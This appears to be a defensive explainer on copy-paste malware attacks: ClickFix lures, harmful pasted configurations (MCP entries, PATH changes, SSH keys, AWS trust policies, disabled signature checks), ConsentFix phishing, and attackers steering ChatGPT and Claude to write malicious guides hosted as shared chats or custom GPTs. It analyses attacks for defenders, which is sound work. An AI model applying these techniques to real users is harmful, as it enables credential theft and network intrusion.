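If the pasted command downloads its script from a web address, a company can block the address or detect the download. Attackers have responded by keeping the script elsewhere. ilsoftware.it's *Microsoft avverte su TerminalFix* describes an earlier variant that fetched malicious code through DNS, the system that translates website names into numerical addresses. Nearly every network has to allow DNS requests, and fewer defenders inspect them. TerminalFix similarly hid its later programs in pictures, so that a filter checking for programs would find only image files.

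In late 2026 some attackers put the first script on the victim's computer before the victim pasted anything. Browsers keep copies of pictures in a folder called the cache, so that pages load faster next time. Mishcon de Reya's *Picture This* (2026) summarises a Microsoft post about hacked sites that served an image with a script hidden inside it. When a victim visited the page, the browser saved the image, including the script, to the cache. The pasted command then searched the cache for a file of the expected size, copied it under a name that marks it as a script, and ran it.

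This gets around the limited space in the Run dialog, and the first script needs no separate download when the victim presses Enter. The attack can still be noticed, because the script contacted a server for more components before it stole browser passwords, and a command that searches a browser's cache is unusual.

Red Code reported a similar chain in December but didn't name the investigations behind its summary. Vega, a security company that studied the technique, did not confirm that the hidden script had run on the machines it examined. Attackers clearly prepared such pages, but it is much less clear how often the method worked.

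### From one paste to a whole network

The victim's losses depend mainly on the payload. Microsoft's *Think before you ClickFix* (2025) reports that the infostealer Lumma was apparently the most common payload in the attacks Microsoft had observed. An infostealer on a home computer can lead to emptied cryptocurrency wallets and strangers getting into the victim's email. Other attacks delivered remote access tools, which let an attacker operate the computer from a distance, or loaders, small programs that bring in more malware. On an office computer, either can be the start of a much larger attack.

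Attackers inside a Windows network usually try to reach the domain controller, the server that decides who may sign in and what they may do, because anyone who controls it can control most of the other machines. Huntress' *ClickFix Won't Die. Neither Will Matanbuchus* describes an intrusion from February 2026 that followed this pattern. A pasted command installed a loader, which brought in a remote access tool. About 17 hours later, the attacker returned, looked up the network's administrators and signed in to a server with a compromised service account, which is an account meant for software. The attacker targeted both domain controllers less than 40 minutes after first moving to another machine.

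The operator also created a new administrator account and set the antivirus software to ignore certain locations. Defenders interrupted the intrusion before it reached its goal. Huntress has only medium confidence that the goal was ransomware or data theft, because it inferred this from similar intrusions.

The attackers in the May case got further. A user pasted the first command on a computer that Huntress wasn't monitoring, and the intrusion was well under way by the time Huntress's software was installed on the affected machines. The attackers repeatedly tried different ways to disable Microsoft Defender, the antivirus program built into Windows, and eventually shut it down. They reached the domain controller and spread a remote access tool to at least 11 machines.

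One of the malicious programs in that case could steal passwords and cookies from Chrome, Firefox and Edge, and give the attacker a hidden desktop to work on. Its loader tried up to 10,000 web addresses in a fixed order to find the attackers' server, so blocking one address would achieve little. But because the order never changed, Huntress could calculate the whole list and publish it for others to block. Huntress, which sells monitoring services, concludes that companies should monitor every machine, and the facts of this case support that advice.

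A single overlooked account can have the same effect as an unwatched computer. In 2026 attackers used a ClickFix page to enter the network of Epe, a Dutch municipality, with one employee's rights. They then gained higher rights through a poorly secured "break glass" account, an emergency account that lets administrators back in when the normal login fails. Such an account needs broad rights to be useful, and administrators sometimes exempt it from the usual login checks so that it works in a crisis.

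### Berlin

The best-known case so far is the August 2026 attack on Berlin's state government. On 7 September, heise online's *BSI erklärt ersten Angriffsvektor auf Berliner Behörden* (2026) reported the first analysis by the BSI, Germany's federal agency for information security. According to the BSI, the attack began with a phishing message, followed by a fake CAPTCHA and a command in the terminal. IT-Administrator's *Berlin-Hack* had earlier called the entry route unsettled and warned against speculation.

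According to Help Net Security's *Berlin refuses to be blackmailed after network breach* (2026), officials believe that data left the network between 7 and 12 August, but the affected departments stayed connected to the state network until 14 August. The criminal group Rhysida listed Berlin on its website and claimed to have 1.44 million files, or 5.79 terabytes. It said that 5,941 of the files contained passwords and that the data included personal information about 12,076 people. These figures come from the blackmailers, who had good reason to make the data sound valuable. The group reportedly demanded 30 bitcoin, about two million euros. Governing Mayor Kai Wegner refused to pay, and Rhysida published the files.

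In traditional ransomware attacks, the attackers encrypt files and demand money for the key. Dalg (2026), in *Berliner Cyberangriff*, reported that the attackers had not encrypted anything in Berlin, so their threat was to publish what they had stolen. The disruption was still severe. Schurter (2026), in *Hackerangriff legt deutsche Behörden lahm*, quoted a complaint in his headline that staff were "practically unable to work". For days the city could not pay housing benefit, according to ntv's *Berlin wird nach Hackerangriff erpresst* (2026). Some of the disruption probably came from disconnecting the departments, which was necessary but cut them off from systems they needed.

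Restoring the computers doesn't undo the publication of the files. IT-Administrator points out that the files may give other criminals real names, telephone numbers and signatures, which they can use to write much more convincing messages to the same offices.

Whoever pasted the command does not deserve all the blame. An expert cited by Dalg suspected that the attackers had not encountered strong security. A large organisation has to expect that somebody will eventually fall for a lure, and one person's mistake shouldn't be enough to expose millions of files.

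### Who uses it, and what they pay

US authorities described Rhysida in 2023 as a group that rents ransomware and servers to affiliates, who carry out attacks and give it part of the proceeds. The name on a ransom demand is therefore not enough to identify who wrote the lure or carried out the attack.

Other suppliers cover the earlier steps. Sellers on criminal forums offer kits that build the fake page, so the buyer only has to choose a design and add a command. The loader in Huntress's February case, Matanbuchus, cost $2,500 a month when its seller first advertised it in 2021. The current version costs $10,000 a month, or $15,000 with its communications hidden in DNS traffic. Huntress says this is three to five times the price of a typical mid-range loader and infers that the buyers are after valuable targets. That seems right, since few people would pay that much to collect passwords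 from random home computers.

State-backed hackers have also adopted ClickFix. The security company Proofpoint reported in April 2025 that groups linked to North Korea, Iran and Russia had tried it over the previous winter. The Iranian group sent emails posing as Microsoft security notices that asked recipients to run PowerShell as an administrator. The technique requires few resources, and using it makes state-backed hackers harder to distinguish from ordinary criminals.

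State use of ClickFix is probably a small part of the total. Microsoft's *Digital Defense Report* (2025) found that only 4% of the breaches it investigated with a known motive were purely espionage. That figure covers all methods of attack, and it may miss some espionage because spies may stay hidden longer than extortionists, who have to reveal themselves to get paid.

### How common is it?

The most dramatic figure comes from the security company CrowdStrike, which Mishcon de Reya quotes as having found a 563% increase during 2025 in incidents involving fake CAPTCHA lures. Mishcon de Reya doesn't give the starting number, so this could be a rise from 100 incidents to 663 or from 10,000 to 66,300. The figure also doesn't correspond exactly to ClickFix, because some ClickFix pages show a fake error or update instead of a CAPTCHA.

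Another popular claim is that ClickFix accounts for 47% of initial access, the first step into a victim's system. Writers usually credit the figure to Microsoft's *Digital Defense Report*, which covers July 2024 to June 2025 according to Microsoft's *Extortion and ransomware drive over half of cyberattacks* (2025). The figure is most likely a share of the attacks that Microsoft Defender Experts, a paid monitoring service, notified its customers about. The report credits this team with observing ClickFix as a method of initial access.

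In the same report, Microsoft's incident response team, which helps organisations after a breach, attributed 10% of its cases to social engineering (deceiving people) and a further 6% to phishing. It identified no entry route in 20%. Microsoft elsewhere gives 28% for phishing and social engineering together, perhaps because that calculation leaves out the cases with no known route. ClickFix is only one kind of social engineering, so on either figure it can hardly have started 47% of these breaches.

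Both sets of figures can still be right. A monitoring service detects many attacks early, including infostealers that it stops within minutes, while incident responders see the cases that went badly wrong. So 47% may fairly describe what Defender Experts dealt with, but it isn't a reliable guide to the share of all breaches, let alone the chance that a given person will fall victim.

All these counts include only the attacks that somebody detected. Security companies mostly see their customers' machines, so the counts include few people at home, although an infostealer can do them a great deal of harm. A company's count can also rise because it improved its detection or won new customers, without any change in what the criminals are doing.

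The largest gap in the data is how many people saw a lure and refused. Someone who finds the instructions odd and closes the tab usually leaves no incident to count. Hudson Rock could count the 108 advertisements on Reddit, but that count doesn't show how many people saw them, opened the page or pasted the command. A thousand infections could come from 2,000 visitors, which would make the lure very persuasive, or from ten million, which would mean that almost everyone recognised it or lost interest. The attackers are better placed to know, since their servers can record page visits and the downloads that follow.

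## How can a pasted configuration do what a command does?

A shell runs a pasted command at once, while a configuration controls how a program behaves when the program reads it later, often every time it starts. Pasting text into a settings file can therefore have the same result as running a command, even if the victim never opens a terminal. Some harmful settings start a program, some give an outsider access, and others redirect traffic or turn off a protection.

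### Settings that start a program

The newest example is the tool-server entry in an AI assistant's settings. The Model Context Protocol, or MCP, is a common standard for connecting assistants to outside tools. A tool server is often a small program on the user's own computer, and the assistant's settings file lists the ones to start. The Model Context Protocol tutorial for Claude Desktop, Anthropic's assistant application, tells users to open this file, replace its contents with a ready-made block and restart the application. Here is a made-up block of the same shape:

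```
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "calendar-helper": {
      "command": "echo",
      "args": ["good morning"]
    }
  }
}
```

The name `calendar-helper` is a label that whoever writes the block can choose freely. The `command` field determines which program starts, and `args` holds the words to pass to it. The application starts `echo` at its next launch, not when the user saves the file. On a Mac, `echo` prints "good morning" and exits. The application then reports a failed connection because `echo` isn't a tool server, but the program has already run. An attacker would name a different program, which would start with the user's rights at every launch.

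In the tutorial's genuine entry, the command is `npx`, which downloads a software package and runs it, and the argument `-y` skips the confirmation. A harmful entry could use the same command and differ only in the package name. The genuine entry also lists the folders that the server may use, but the application only passes this list to the server, and a malicious server could ignore it. Claude asks the user before each action it takes through the server, but this doesn't cover what the server does by itself.

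Applications can ask for approval before they start a new server, but flaws in this check can let a harmful command through. Cursor, a code editor with a built-in assistant, asked for approval when a shared project contained a new entry, but in 2025 Check Point Research found that it tied the approval to the entry's name alone. A collaborator could add a harmless entry, wait for the victim to approve it and then change the command, which Cursor would run without asking again. Cursor acknowledged the flaw in an advisory quoted in The Hacker News' *Cursor AI Code Editor Vulnerability* (2025), and has since fixed it. NVD's *CVE-2025-64106 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, describes another flaw in Cursor 1.7.28 and earlier, where an installation link could hide the command from the user who accepted it.

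An approval prompt can mislead even when it works properly. The security company Proofpoint built a demonstration called CursorJack, in which an installation link could carry any name, such as that of a well-known Microsoft service, and nothing checked that the link came from the company named. The victim still had to click the link and approve the installation, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *'CursorJack’ Attack Path Exposes Code Execution Risk in AI Development Environment*.

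Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* requires applications with one-click installation to show the entire command and get the user's approval first. The proposal behind this rule warned that users grow comfortable running commands labelled "MCP servers" without examining them. The rule doesn't cover configurations that users paste into the settings file by hand. Claude Code, Anthropic's assistant for programmers, goes further with shared projects. According to Anthropic, it won't use any server listed in a project's own file until the user approves it, and a downloaded project can't approve its own servers.

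Older settings work in the same way. The shell zsh reads a start-up file called `.zshrc` whenever the user opens a terminal window, and runs every line in it. Honest installers often ask users to add a line such as this:

```
export PATH="$HOME/tools:$PATH"
```

A pasted configuration can put a folder called `tools` at the front of the search path. Anyone who can place programs in that folder can then replace a familiar command, much as intruders did with `ls` on shared Unix machines in the 1980s.

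On company servers, the harmful configuration may be a manifest for Kubernetes, a system that runs software across many machines. The manifest describes what should be running, and an administrator can load one directly from a web address. Kubernetes then keeps those programs running, so if someone stops a harmful one but leaves its entry in place, Kubernetes starts another copy.

### Settings that let someone in

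Administrators usually sign in to remote servers with SSH, an encrypted connection. Each account can have a list of public keys, and anyone who holds a matching private key can sign in without a password. A fake support technician can ask a user to add "our key", which is one line of random-looking text. Changing the account's password doesn't remove the key. The attacker can use it only if the machine is reachable and accepts SSH connections, so the danger is greater on a server than on a home laptop.

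A cloud account can be opened to an outsider without touching the victim's computer at all. In Amazon's cloud, a role is a set of permissions that people or programs can borrow for a short time, and a trust policy lists who may borrow it. The important line can be as short as this:

```
"Principal": { "AWS": "111122223333" }
```

The twelve digits are an account number, in this case one from Amazon's documentation. If a victim pastes in a policy with an attacker's number, the attacker can use the role to do whatever it permits. This leaves nothing on the victim's computer for antivirus software to find. The request may not seem strange, because legitimate monitoring services also ask customers to create such roles.

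### Pasted sign-in codes and addresses

Some attacks obtain access without changing a settings file. The victim pastes or types a code that connects an attacker's program to their account.

Televisions and similar devices have no convenient keyboard, so owners connect them to an account by opening the real sign-in page on a phone and entering a short code shown on the device. In device-code phishing, the attacker starts this process on their own machine and sends the code to the victim, perhaps claiming that it is needed to join a meeting. The victim enters the code on the real page and signs in, which gives the attacker's machine access to the victim's account. Microsoft reported in February 2025 that a group it calls Storm-2372 had been doing this since August 2024.

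ConsentFix reverses the direction of the paste, with the victim copying a code from the genuine service into the attacker's page. In *ConsentFix*, Jennings (2025) described the first known campaign, which his employer, the browser security company Push Security, had intercepted. Victims found a hacked website through Google Search, where a fake Cloudflare check asked for their email address. If the address belonged to an organisation on the attackers' list, the page showed a "Sign In" button that opened Microsoft's real sign-in page.

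After the victim signed in or picked an account, Microsoft sent the browser to `localhost`, which refers to the user's own computer. The full address contained a code meant for Azure CLI, Microsoft's command-line program for managing its cloud. The attackers told the victim to copy the address and paste it into their page. They could then exchange the code for a token that gave them access to the account.

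A web service that connects to an account this way normally has to present its own secret along with the code. Desktop programs can't keep such a secret, so they need only the code. Organisations that use Microsoft's cloud also trust Azure CLI by default, and the restrictions on unfamiliar apps don't apply to it.

Passkeys don't help here. They normally defeat phishing because they work only on the genuine site, but in this attack the victim is on the genuine site, and someone who is already signed in may not need a passkey at all. The sign-in also comes from the victim's own internet connection, so its location looks normal. Jennings suggests looking for Azure CLI sign-ins by people who are neither administrators nor developers. NVISO's *ConsentFix (a.k.a. AuthCodeFix)* (2026) explains the mechanism the same way and adds that other applications are vulnerable too. Push says it blocked the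 attack before its customers interacted with the pages, so its account is good evidence of how the attack works but not of how many people fell for it.

### Settings that redirect traffic or remove a check

A computer's DNS setting determines which server it uses to look up the numerical addresses of websites. An attacker who persuades someone to change it can send them to the wrong machine even when they type the correct name. Encryption limits the damage, because the attacker normally can't prove ownership of the name, so the browser shows a warning. The attacker can still see which names the computer looks up and can interfere with unencrypted connections.

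Other settings disable a check. On some Linux systems, `gpgcheck=0` stops the package installer from verifying signatures, which removes the main advantage of signed packages over a script from the web. Firouzi, Bhatt and Ghafari (2026), in *Can Developers rely on LLMs for Secure IaC Development?*, gave ChatGPT a settings file that contained this line and made the installer fetch packages over an unencrypted connection. They asked for new, secure code, but the answer still turned signature checks off, without a warning.

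The same study found a server configuration on GitHub, the code-sharing site, that turned off SSH's check on the identity of the server at the other end. People do this to get rid of an inconvenient error message, so such a line is weak evidence of an attack.

### Why a setting is harder to judge than a command

A user who pastes a command may notice a strange window or a slow computer within seconds. A tool-server entry does nothing until the next restart, and a trust policy may have no visible effect until the attacker uses it weeks later. By then the victim may not connect the problem to what they pasted. Settings also persist, so deleting a malicious program won't help much if a line that runs at start-up downloads it again.

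Reading the text may not be enough either. A line that sends a folder of passwords to a strange address is suspicious in itself, but nobody can tell from a twelve-digit account number whether the account belongs to the company's monitoring service or to a criminal. The reader has to look the number up elsewhere, and in a long file they first have to notice that it needs checking.

AI reviewers may miss more insecure settings when they are given longer text. Firouzi and colleagues asked GPT-4o and Gemini 2.0 Flash to analyse insecure settings from a security perspective. With short snippets from Stack Overflow, a question-and-answer site for programmers, GPT-4o found the problem in 80% of cases and Gemini in 71%. With complete files from GitHub, GPT-4o found it in 42% and Gemini in 51%.

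Length can't explain all of this difference. The GitHub files included 75 whose only listed problem was a suspicious comment, such as a note to fix something later, while the snippets included none. GPT-4o missed nearly all 75. Without those files, it would still have found only about 52% of the problems in the complete files. More detailed instructions helped considerably, but only someone who already knows how to ask would give them.

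Experts disagree too. In *Compared to What?* (Shaw, 2026), three cloud-security practitioners rated descriptions of cloud set-up tasks. Their agreement on whether a task involved a meaningful security decision was 0.059, where 0 is chance and 1 is perfect. They rated tasks rather than finished settings, but the result suggests that an expert's second opinion on a configuration may be less reliable than it seems.

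Settings are easier to inspect than commands because they stay in place. A company that keeps its settings files in a shared version-control system can see who changed which line, have a colleague review the change and restore the old version. Someone who edits a file on their own laptop usually can't do any of this.

### What assistants write when nobody is attacking

Many companies now describe their cloud servers, storage and permissions in text files, and a program such as Terraform builds whatever the files describe. AI assistants write some of these files, and several studies have measured how secure the files are when no attacker is involved.

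Shaw gave 100 tasks to nine models in 12 set-ups and obtained 1,196 files. He ran three security scanners on these and on 634 files written by people. Short files have more findings per resource (a server or a storage area, for example) whoever writes them, so he compared files of similar size. The assistants' files had 3.21 to 3.87 times as many findings per resource as the human ones. The ratio was 4.9 for files with one resource. For files with 20 or more, it was 1.4, which could be due to chance.

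However, 52 of the tasks asked for something insecure, such as an open SSH port, so an assistant that produced it was following instructions. Without these tasks, every set-up still had at least 2.4 times the human rate. Only 15 tasks asked for neither secure nor insecure settings, and Shaw concludes that these are too few to show what assistants do by default. The human files came from three public collections that include reference examples, which may be tidier than the average engineer's work. About half of the findings with a severity rating were rated low or informational.

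Vargas, Mansilha and Kreutz (2026) tested the default more directly in *Security-First Evaluation of Text-to-Terraform*. They gave seven models 17 tasks for Amazon's cloud, with prompts that left out security, gave general advice about it or listed the exact rules to satisfy. When the prompt left out security, at most five of any model's files passed the scanner Trivy and at most one passed another scanner, Checkov, although four of the models had over 100 files in the comparison. With the exact rules, 92.5% of Claude Opus 4's files passed Trivy but only 23.1% passed Checkov.

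Much of that gap comes from the different standards for passing. A file failed Checkov if it broke a single rule, while the study's test for Trivy ignored minor problems. A file described as insecure in these studies therefore often lacks some recommended protection, but a criminal might not be able to exploit that. More detailed instructions didn't always help. After general advice, 51 of GPT-5.4's files passed Trivy, compared with only 24 after the detailed list.

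Firouzi and colleagues found that only 7% of the files that GPT-4o and Gemini 2.0 Flash wrote were secure. They built their 89 scenarios to invite insecure answers, for example by asking for an outdated method of protecting passwords, so this figure doesn't estimate the rate in ordinary use. The more useful result is that 75% of GPT-4o's answers and 56% of Gemini's were insecure and gave no warning. Adding the word "secure" to the request raised GPT-4o's share of secure files to 17% and made little difference to Gemini's.

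People write insecure settings too. *GenSIaC* (2025) cites an earlier study in which 10.4% to 40.1% of infrastructure scripts, depending on the project, had at least one weakness. Those scripts weren't responses to deliberately difficult requests, so comparing that range with the 7% would be unfair to the assistants. Shaw's comparison is fairer because it used the same scanners on both groups.

These results make it reasonable to run a scanner on any settings file an assistant has written, and Vargas and colleagues recommend using more than one. A scanner is good at finding an open port or missing encryption, but it can't determine whether the account number in a trust policy belongs to a stranger unless it has a list of the accounts the company trusts.

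## How do attackers publish malicious instructions under an AI company's own address?

Since late 2025, attackers have published harmful commands on the websites of OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI, which make the assistants ChatGPT, Claude and Grok. Each company lets users publish pages on its site, so the attackers didn't have to hack it.

### What a stranger can publish

The simplest such page is a shared conversation. When a user presses "Share" in a chat with an assistant, the company puts a copy of the chat at a public link. Anyone with the link to a shared ChatGPT conversation can read it, according to the OpenAI documentation cited in eWeek's *ChatGPT Share Links Abused Through Real OpenAI URLs*. Huntress' *The AI Attack Surface* adds that search engines can find these pages, for instance when somebody posts the link on a forum.

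A shared conversation shows what the assistant told someone else, who may have steered its answers. Kaspersky's *Infostealer has entered the chat* describes attackers who worded their prompts to make ChatGPT produce the installation guide they wanted, then cleaned up the earlier dialogue, leaving what looked like ordinary help.

ChatGPT labels these pages. The line above that guide read "This is a copy of a conversation between ChatGPT & anonymous", which was accurate, but readers had to work out that "anonymous" might have got ChatGPT to write almost anything. Claude's shared pages show a display name that the sharer chooses. Huntress' *How a Google Search for Claude Led to MacSync* describes an attack in which the name was "Apple Support", so the label made the page more convincing instead of showing that a stranger had shared it.

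Published pages don't have to look like a chat. Claude can build a small web page or program, called an artifact, which the user can publish at Claude's address. Anthropic doesn't vet artifacts but labels each one "Content is user-generated and unverified." ChatGPT can also display a page from code. *LLMShare* (Maharaj, 2026) describes a page at ChatGPT's address with a message claiming that the website was overloaded and offering a desktop application instead. The only visible signs that a user had made the page were two buttons above the message, "Show code" and "Remix with ChatGPT". The download was a malicious program, so no one had to paste anything, but the case shows how much of such a page an attacker can design.

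OpenAI also lets users make their own versions of ChatGPT, called custom GPTs, with a name, standing instructions and reference files, and open them to other people. The builder's instructions apply to every conversation with that version, so a builder can make it give visitors the same reply whatever they type. The page shows the chosen name and the builder's profile, according to ETV Bharat's *Hackers Exploit ChatGPT Custom GPTs In ClickFix Malware Attacks* (2026).

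### A search for disk space

On 5 December 2025, Huntress examined an alert about Atomic macOS Stealer (AMOS), an infostealer for Macs. Huntress' *AMOS Stealer Exploits AI Trust* traces the infection to a Google search for "Clear disk space on macOS", rather than to a source its analysts had expected, such as a phishing email or a doctored installer. Near the top of the results were links to a ChatGPT conversation and a Grok conversation, both with advice on freeing up storage. Similar searches, such as "free up storage on Mac", brought up similar links.

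The ChatGPT conversation that the user opened was real, and the attacker had held it and then shared it. It contained numbered steps, a terminal command, and assurances that the command wouldn't touch personal data or system settings. Base64 encoding hid the web address in the command. The Grok conversation gave the same instructions with a slightly different encoded address.

The pasted command fetched a script that prompted the user for the "System Password". The script quietly checked the password with a built-in macOS tool, saved it in a hidden file and passed it to `sudo`. The attackers could then run commands as root without further input from the user.

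The Eclectic Light Company's *How online search and AI can install malware* describes following the same steps on a virtual Mac and compares the false password request with the real one. The real prompt reads "Password:", followed by a key symbol, and nothing appears as the user types. The false one read "System Password:" and displayed the password in plain text. These differences are good clues for someone who uses `sudo` every week, but not for someone who opens the terminal once a year to clear some space and doesn't know what the real prompt looks like.

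AMOS was built to collect browser passwords and login cookies, secrets from the Mac's keychain, and files from cryptocurrency wallets. If it found Ledger Wallet or Trezor Suite, two programs for managing cryptocurrency, it replaced them with fakes that asked for the owner's recovery phrase. Anyone who has that phrase controls the money, and the owner can't reset it like a password. The attackers also installed a start-up item so that the malware would run again after a restart. If the user stopped the malware, a background script started it again within a second.

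Advertising is a more likely explanation for the two links' position in Google's results than manipulated rankings, although the attackers may have used both. Huntress calls the links "highly ranked" and believes that the attackers manipulated Google's ranking, but it also places them above the organic (unpaid) results, where Google usually puts advertisements. The Eclectic Light Company found the ChatGPT link at the top of the sponsored results. The remedy depends on the method used, because Google can check advertisers before it takes their money, but anyone can try to climb the ordinary rankings.

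Huntress also said at first that the attack was not ClickFix. In August 2026 it called the same instructions "ClickFix-like", and another of its articles counts them as ClickFix without qualification. Its first description was the most precise, because the conversation contained no fake check or error and the user was looking for help with a real problem. It was still a copy-paste attack, but an employee whose training covers only fake CAPTCHAs might not recognise it.

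### The same method with other bait

In the case Kaspersky described, people who searched Google for "chatgpt atlas", OpenAI's new web browser, could see a sponsored link to a page on ChatGPT's own site, with a title offering Atlas for the Mac. The link opened the cleaned-up conversation, which contained instructions to paste one line into the terminal. That line ran a script that asked for the system password until the user entered the right one. The script installed AMOS and a second program that let the attackers control the Mac remotely.

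When Kaspersky asked ChatGPT whether these instructions were safe to follow, ChatGPT said they weren't. ChatGPT had also written the published guide, but the attackers had steered that conversation.

In March 2026 the security company Sophos reported three campaigns, summarised by The Hacker News, that spread another Mac infostealer, MacSync. In November 2025, advertisements led to a fake Atlas page on Google Sites, Google's free website builder. In December, people who searched for ways to clean up a Mac found sponsored links to shared ChatGPT conversations, which sent them to imitation GitHub pages containing the command. The third campaign, in February 2026, delivered a new version of MacSync that ran more of its code in memory. The Hacker News doesn't mention shared conversations in that campaign.

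SC Media's *ClickFix campaigns target macOS users via MacSync infostealer* reports Sophos's view that the three campaigns became progressively more sophisticated. The malware did change, but Sophos couldn't tell whether the same people were behind all three. One of the three campaigns used shared conversations, which is too little evidence to show that attackers in general were moving to them.

Trend Micro's *Threat Actors Abuse claude.ai Shared Chat for ClickFix Malvertising Campaign* has better evidence of one operation changing its method. It covers six waves of Google advertisements between 8 April and 14 June 2026. (It gives the duration as seven weeks, but those dates are nearly ten weeks apart.) Most of the advertisements targeted people looking for AI programming tools, while others offered to clean up a Mac. In the first four waves, the advertisements led to pages the attackers had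 built themselves, mainly on GitLab Pages, a free hosting service.

On 6 May the operators began sending people to shared Claude conversations instead. Trend Micro found at least 45 of these conversations in the fifth wave and at least 61 in the sixth, when they accounted for all the activity it observed. The operators presented them as guides from "Apple Support" or "Corda Team", with instructions for Mac users to paste a command containing an encoded address. The command ran a script that installed MacSync unless it found a Russian keyboard layout. On 12 May Malwarebytes' *Fake Claude search results lure Mac users into ClickFix attack* (2026) warned of the same kind of lure for people who searched for "Claude Mac download".

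Trend Micro counted 106 malicious hostnames (the part of a web address that names the site), but 92 were on GitLab Pages, so the count mostly covers the period before attackers used shared conversations. Trend Micro also refers to "over 2,000 victims", but the attack waves it reports add up to 2,530 "traffic hits", which are visits, not infections. About a quarter of these visits (626) were to shared Claude conversations.

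Visits fell as the operators moved to Claude's address, from about 125 a day in the first wave to about 33 in the fifth and about 13 in the sixth. Trend Micro calls the move an escalation, and the new pages may well have persuaded a larger share of their visitors. But its figures don't include how many people ran the command in either period, so it's unclear from them whether the move helped the attackers.

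Huntress has confirmed an infection from July 2026. A customer searched Google for how to install Claude on a Mac, clicked a sponsored result and arrived at the shared conversation signed "Apple Support". The command in it installed MacSync, which steals browser logins and the keys developers use to access servers and cloud accounts. The customer shut the computer down when something seemed wrong. Investigators would normally have lost some evidence as a result, but they downloaded a sample of the malware from the attackers' server.

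Other attackers have since used this method. According to Huntress, the security company Cato Networks found a variant in August 2026 that offered a fake download of Codex, OpenAI's programming assistant. PhishFort's *How a Real ChatGPT Link Delivers Phishing via a Fake Codex Install* describes a shared ChatGPT conversation that also offered a fake Codex download.

Shared conversations still seem to play a small part in crime that exploits AI brands. Sophos' *Fake AI, real malware* reviews 38 AI-related cases from the company's monitoring service, mostly from the year ending June 2026. In 30 of them, attackers imitated AI software, largely through fake websites and installers. Sophos mentions only one case with a ChatGPT share link. The cases come only from Sophos customers, but the proportion suggests that an ordinary fake website still works well enough for most attackers.

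### One reply to every question

In September 2026 attackers used a custom GPT called "Plus 5.6". TechRadar's *Hackers host fake ChatGPT model on its official website* notes that the name resembled those of OpenAI's own models. People who searched Google for "chatgpt" could see a sponsored link to it. SC Media's *Malicious ChatGPT Custom GPTs lead to ClickFix attack* reports that the builder had set the GPT to answer every prompt with the same message, which said that the main address had limited availability and that users should continue at a "backup domain".

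The backup address was a Google Sites page with a fake Cloudflare check, and the rest of the attack was ordinary ClickFix. The pasted command installed a remote access tool, which the attackers loaded through a genuine, signed Canon program. The tool let them watch the victim's screen and switch on the camera and microphone.

This lure has an advantage over a shared conversation because visitors type their own question and get an answer, much as they would expect from ChatGPT. It is also easier to expose, because a second, unrelated question gets the same reply, although a visitor who believes the service is down may not ask one. The page named its creator as a "community builder", which ConsumerAffairs' *Fake ChatGPT scam uses trusted websites to trick users into installing malware* calls an important clue. That clue helps only people who know that strangers can build versions of ChatGPT.

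Huntress linked at least 40 incidents to the Google Sites domain and confirmed that two of them came through a custom GPT, according to Help Net Security's *Malicious Custom GPT on chatgpt.com lures users into installing a RAT* (2026). The others may also have started with a custom GPT, or with some other link to the domain. *Attackers Combine ChatGPT Feature Abuse With ClickFix to Deliver RAT* (Palmer, 2026) describes all 40 as infections, but Huntress called them "incidents", and a monitoring service may stop an attack before the malware takes hold.

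Island, a company that sells a browser for businesses, had seen the trick earlier. Over three days in August, it got an identical "high traffic" message, with a link to a backup address, from two custom GPTs. Cybernews' *850+ fake ChatGPT ads on Google trick Windows users into installing malware* reports that Island connected the wider operation to 26 imitations of ChatGPT and 71 Google advertising campaigns over three months. Island found NetSupport, a commercial remote-control program that criminals often misuse. Huntress found a different tool, so two groups may have been using the same lure.

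Island also counted about 850 arrivals at a page from paid advertisements. Tom's Guide's *Security researchers discover fake ChatGPT ads that trick you into downloading malware* misreports these as 850 advertisements, as does the Cybernews headline. Island cautioned that the arrivals are not confirmed infections, and its data doesn't show how many people were affected.

### Why checking the address fails

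For years the standard advice has been to read the web address before trusting a page. This catches a misspelled imitation of a company's site, because the attacker doesn't control the real one. It fails when a company lets the public publish on the same site as its product. These made-up addresses show the problem:

```
https://assistant.example.invalid/              the company's product
https://assistant.example.invalid/share/7f3a    a stranger's conversation
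```

Both belong to the same company, and the browser shows a valid certificate for both. A certificate confirms which site the browser has reached, but not who wrote the text there. Someone who knows the format can recognize a shared conversation from the part of the address after the slash, but Kaspersky found that the advertisement for the Atlas guide didn't show the full address.

Security software has a similar problem. Many filters rate websites by reputation, and ChatGPT and Claude have excellent reputations. On GitLab Pages, each of the attackers' sites had its own hostname, so a company could block one without blocking the rest, but every shared Claude conversation has the same hostname as Claude. A filter that can read only the hostname has to block all of Claude or none of it, and a company whose staff use Claude is unlikely to block it.

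Kaspersky lists earlier, similar abuse of Dropbox, Google Docs and GitHub, which also let users put their own material at a trusted address. A shared document obviously comes from another user, but a shared conversation has the layout and tone of an assistant that many people already ask for commands.

Checking the address still helps because it exposes cruder fakes, and a page on a site where only the owner can publish is different from a page that anyone can publish. But a correct address on an AI company's site doesn't show that a command is safe. The command itself may contain the harmful address in encoded form.

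### Takedowns and returns

OpenAI had removed "Plus 5.6" by 25 September, after Huntress reported it. Two days later Huntress found another custom GPT from the same campaign, which delivered the same remote access tool through a different signed program. On 29 September Help Net Security found that the second GPT was still online but no longer led to the malicious page. According to Huntress, the attackers were already working on a new installer. They can easily replace a removed custom GPT, since they need only a new name and the same few lines of instructions.

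Anthropic went somewhat further, banning the accounts responsible and disabling the shared conversations when Trend Micro reported them. It also said that it was adding protections against abuse of the sharing feature, but Trend Micro doesn't explain what they are or when they took effect. Trend Micro's record has a gap between 14 May, when the fifth wave ended, and 21 May, when advertisements for new shared conversations began. Without a date for Anthropic's response, it's unclear whether the response caused this gap, and the infection in July doesn't prove that the protections failed.

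A takedown may also come too late or remove only part of the attack. Huntress says these lures often last only hours or days but can draw considerable attention in that time. In July it reported a malicious Claude artifact that posed as a download page and had hit more than 29 organisations. The artifact was gone by 22 July, but Huntress kept seeing incidents through August from the outside address the artifact had sent people to, on a server Anthropic couldn't shut down.

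Huntress reports no response from xAI to the Grok conversation. Google stopped showing the sponsored links from the December case while The Eclectic Light Company was preparing its article. However, ads for other lures hosted on AI companies' sites were still appearing in September 2026. Tom's Guide asked Google about Island's findings and had received no answer when it published.

PhishFort, which sells protection against phishing, criticises Google for accepting such advertisements when two security services owned by Google's parent company already flagged the domains involved as malicious. The criticism is partly fair. A simple check of the link's destination would have found nothing wrong, because the advertisement led to ChatGPT's genuine site and the flagged domain was hidden in the command. To find it, Google would have had to open the conversation, decode the command and look up the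 result, which a large advertising company could do.

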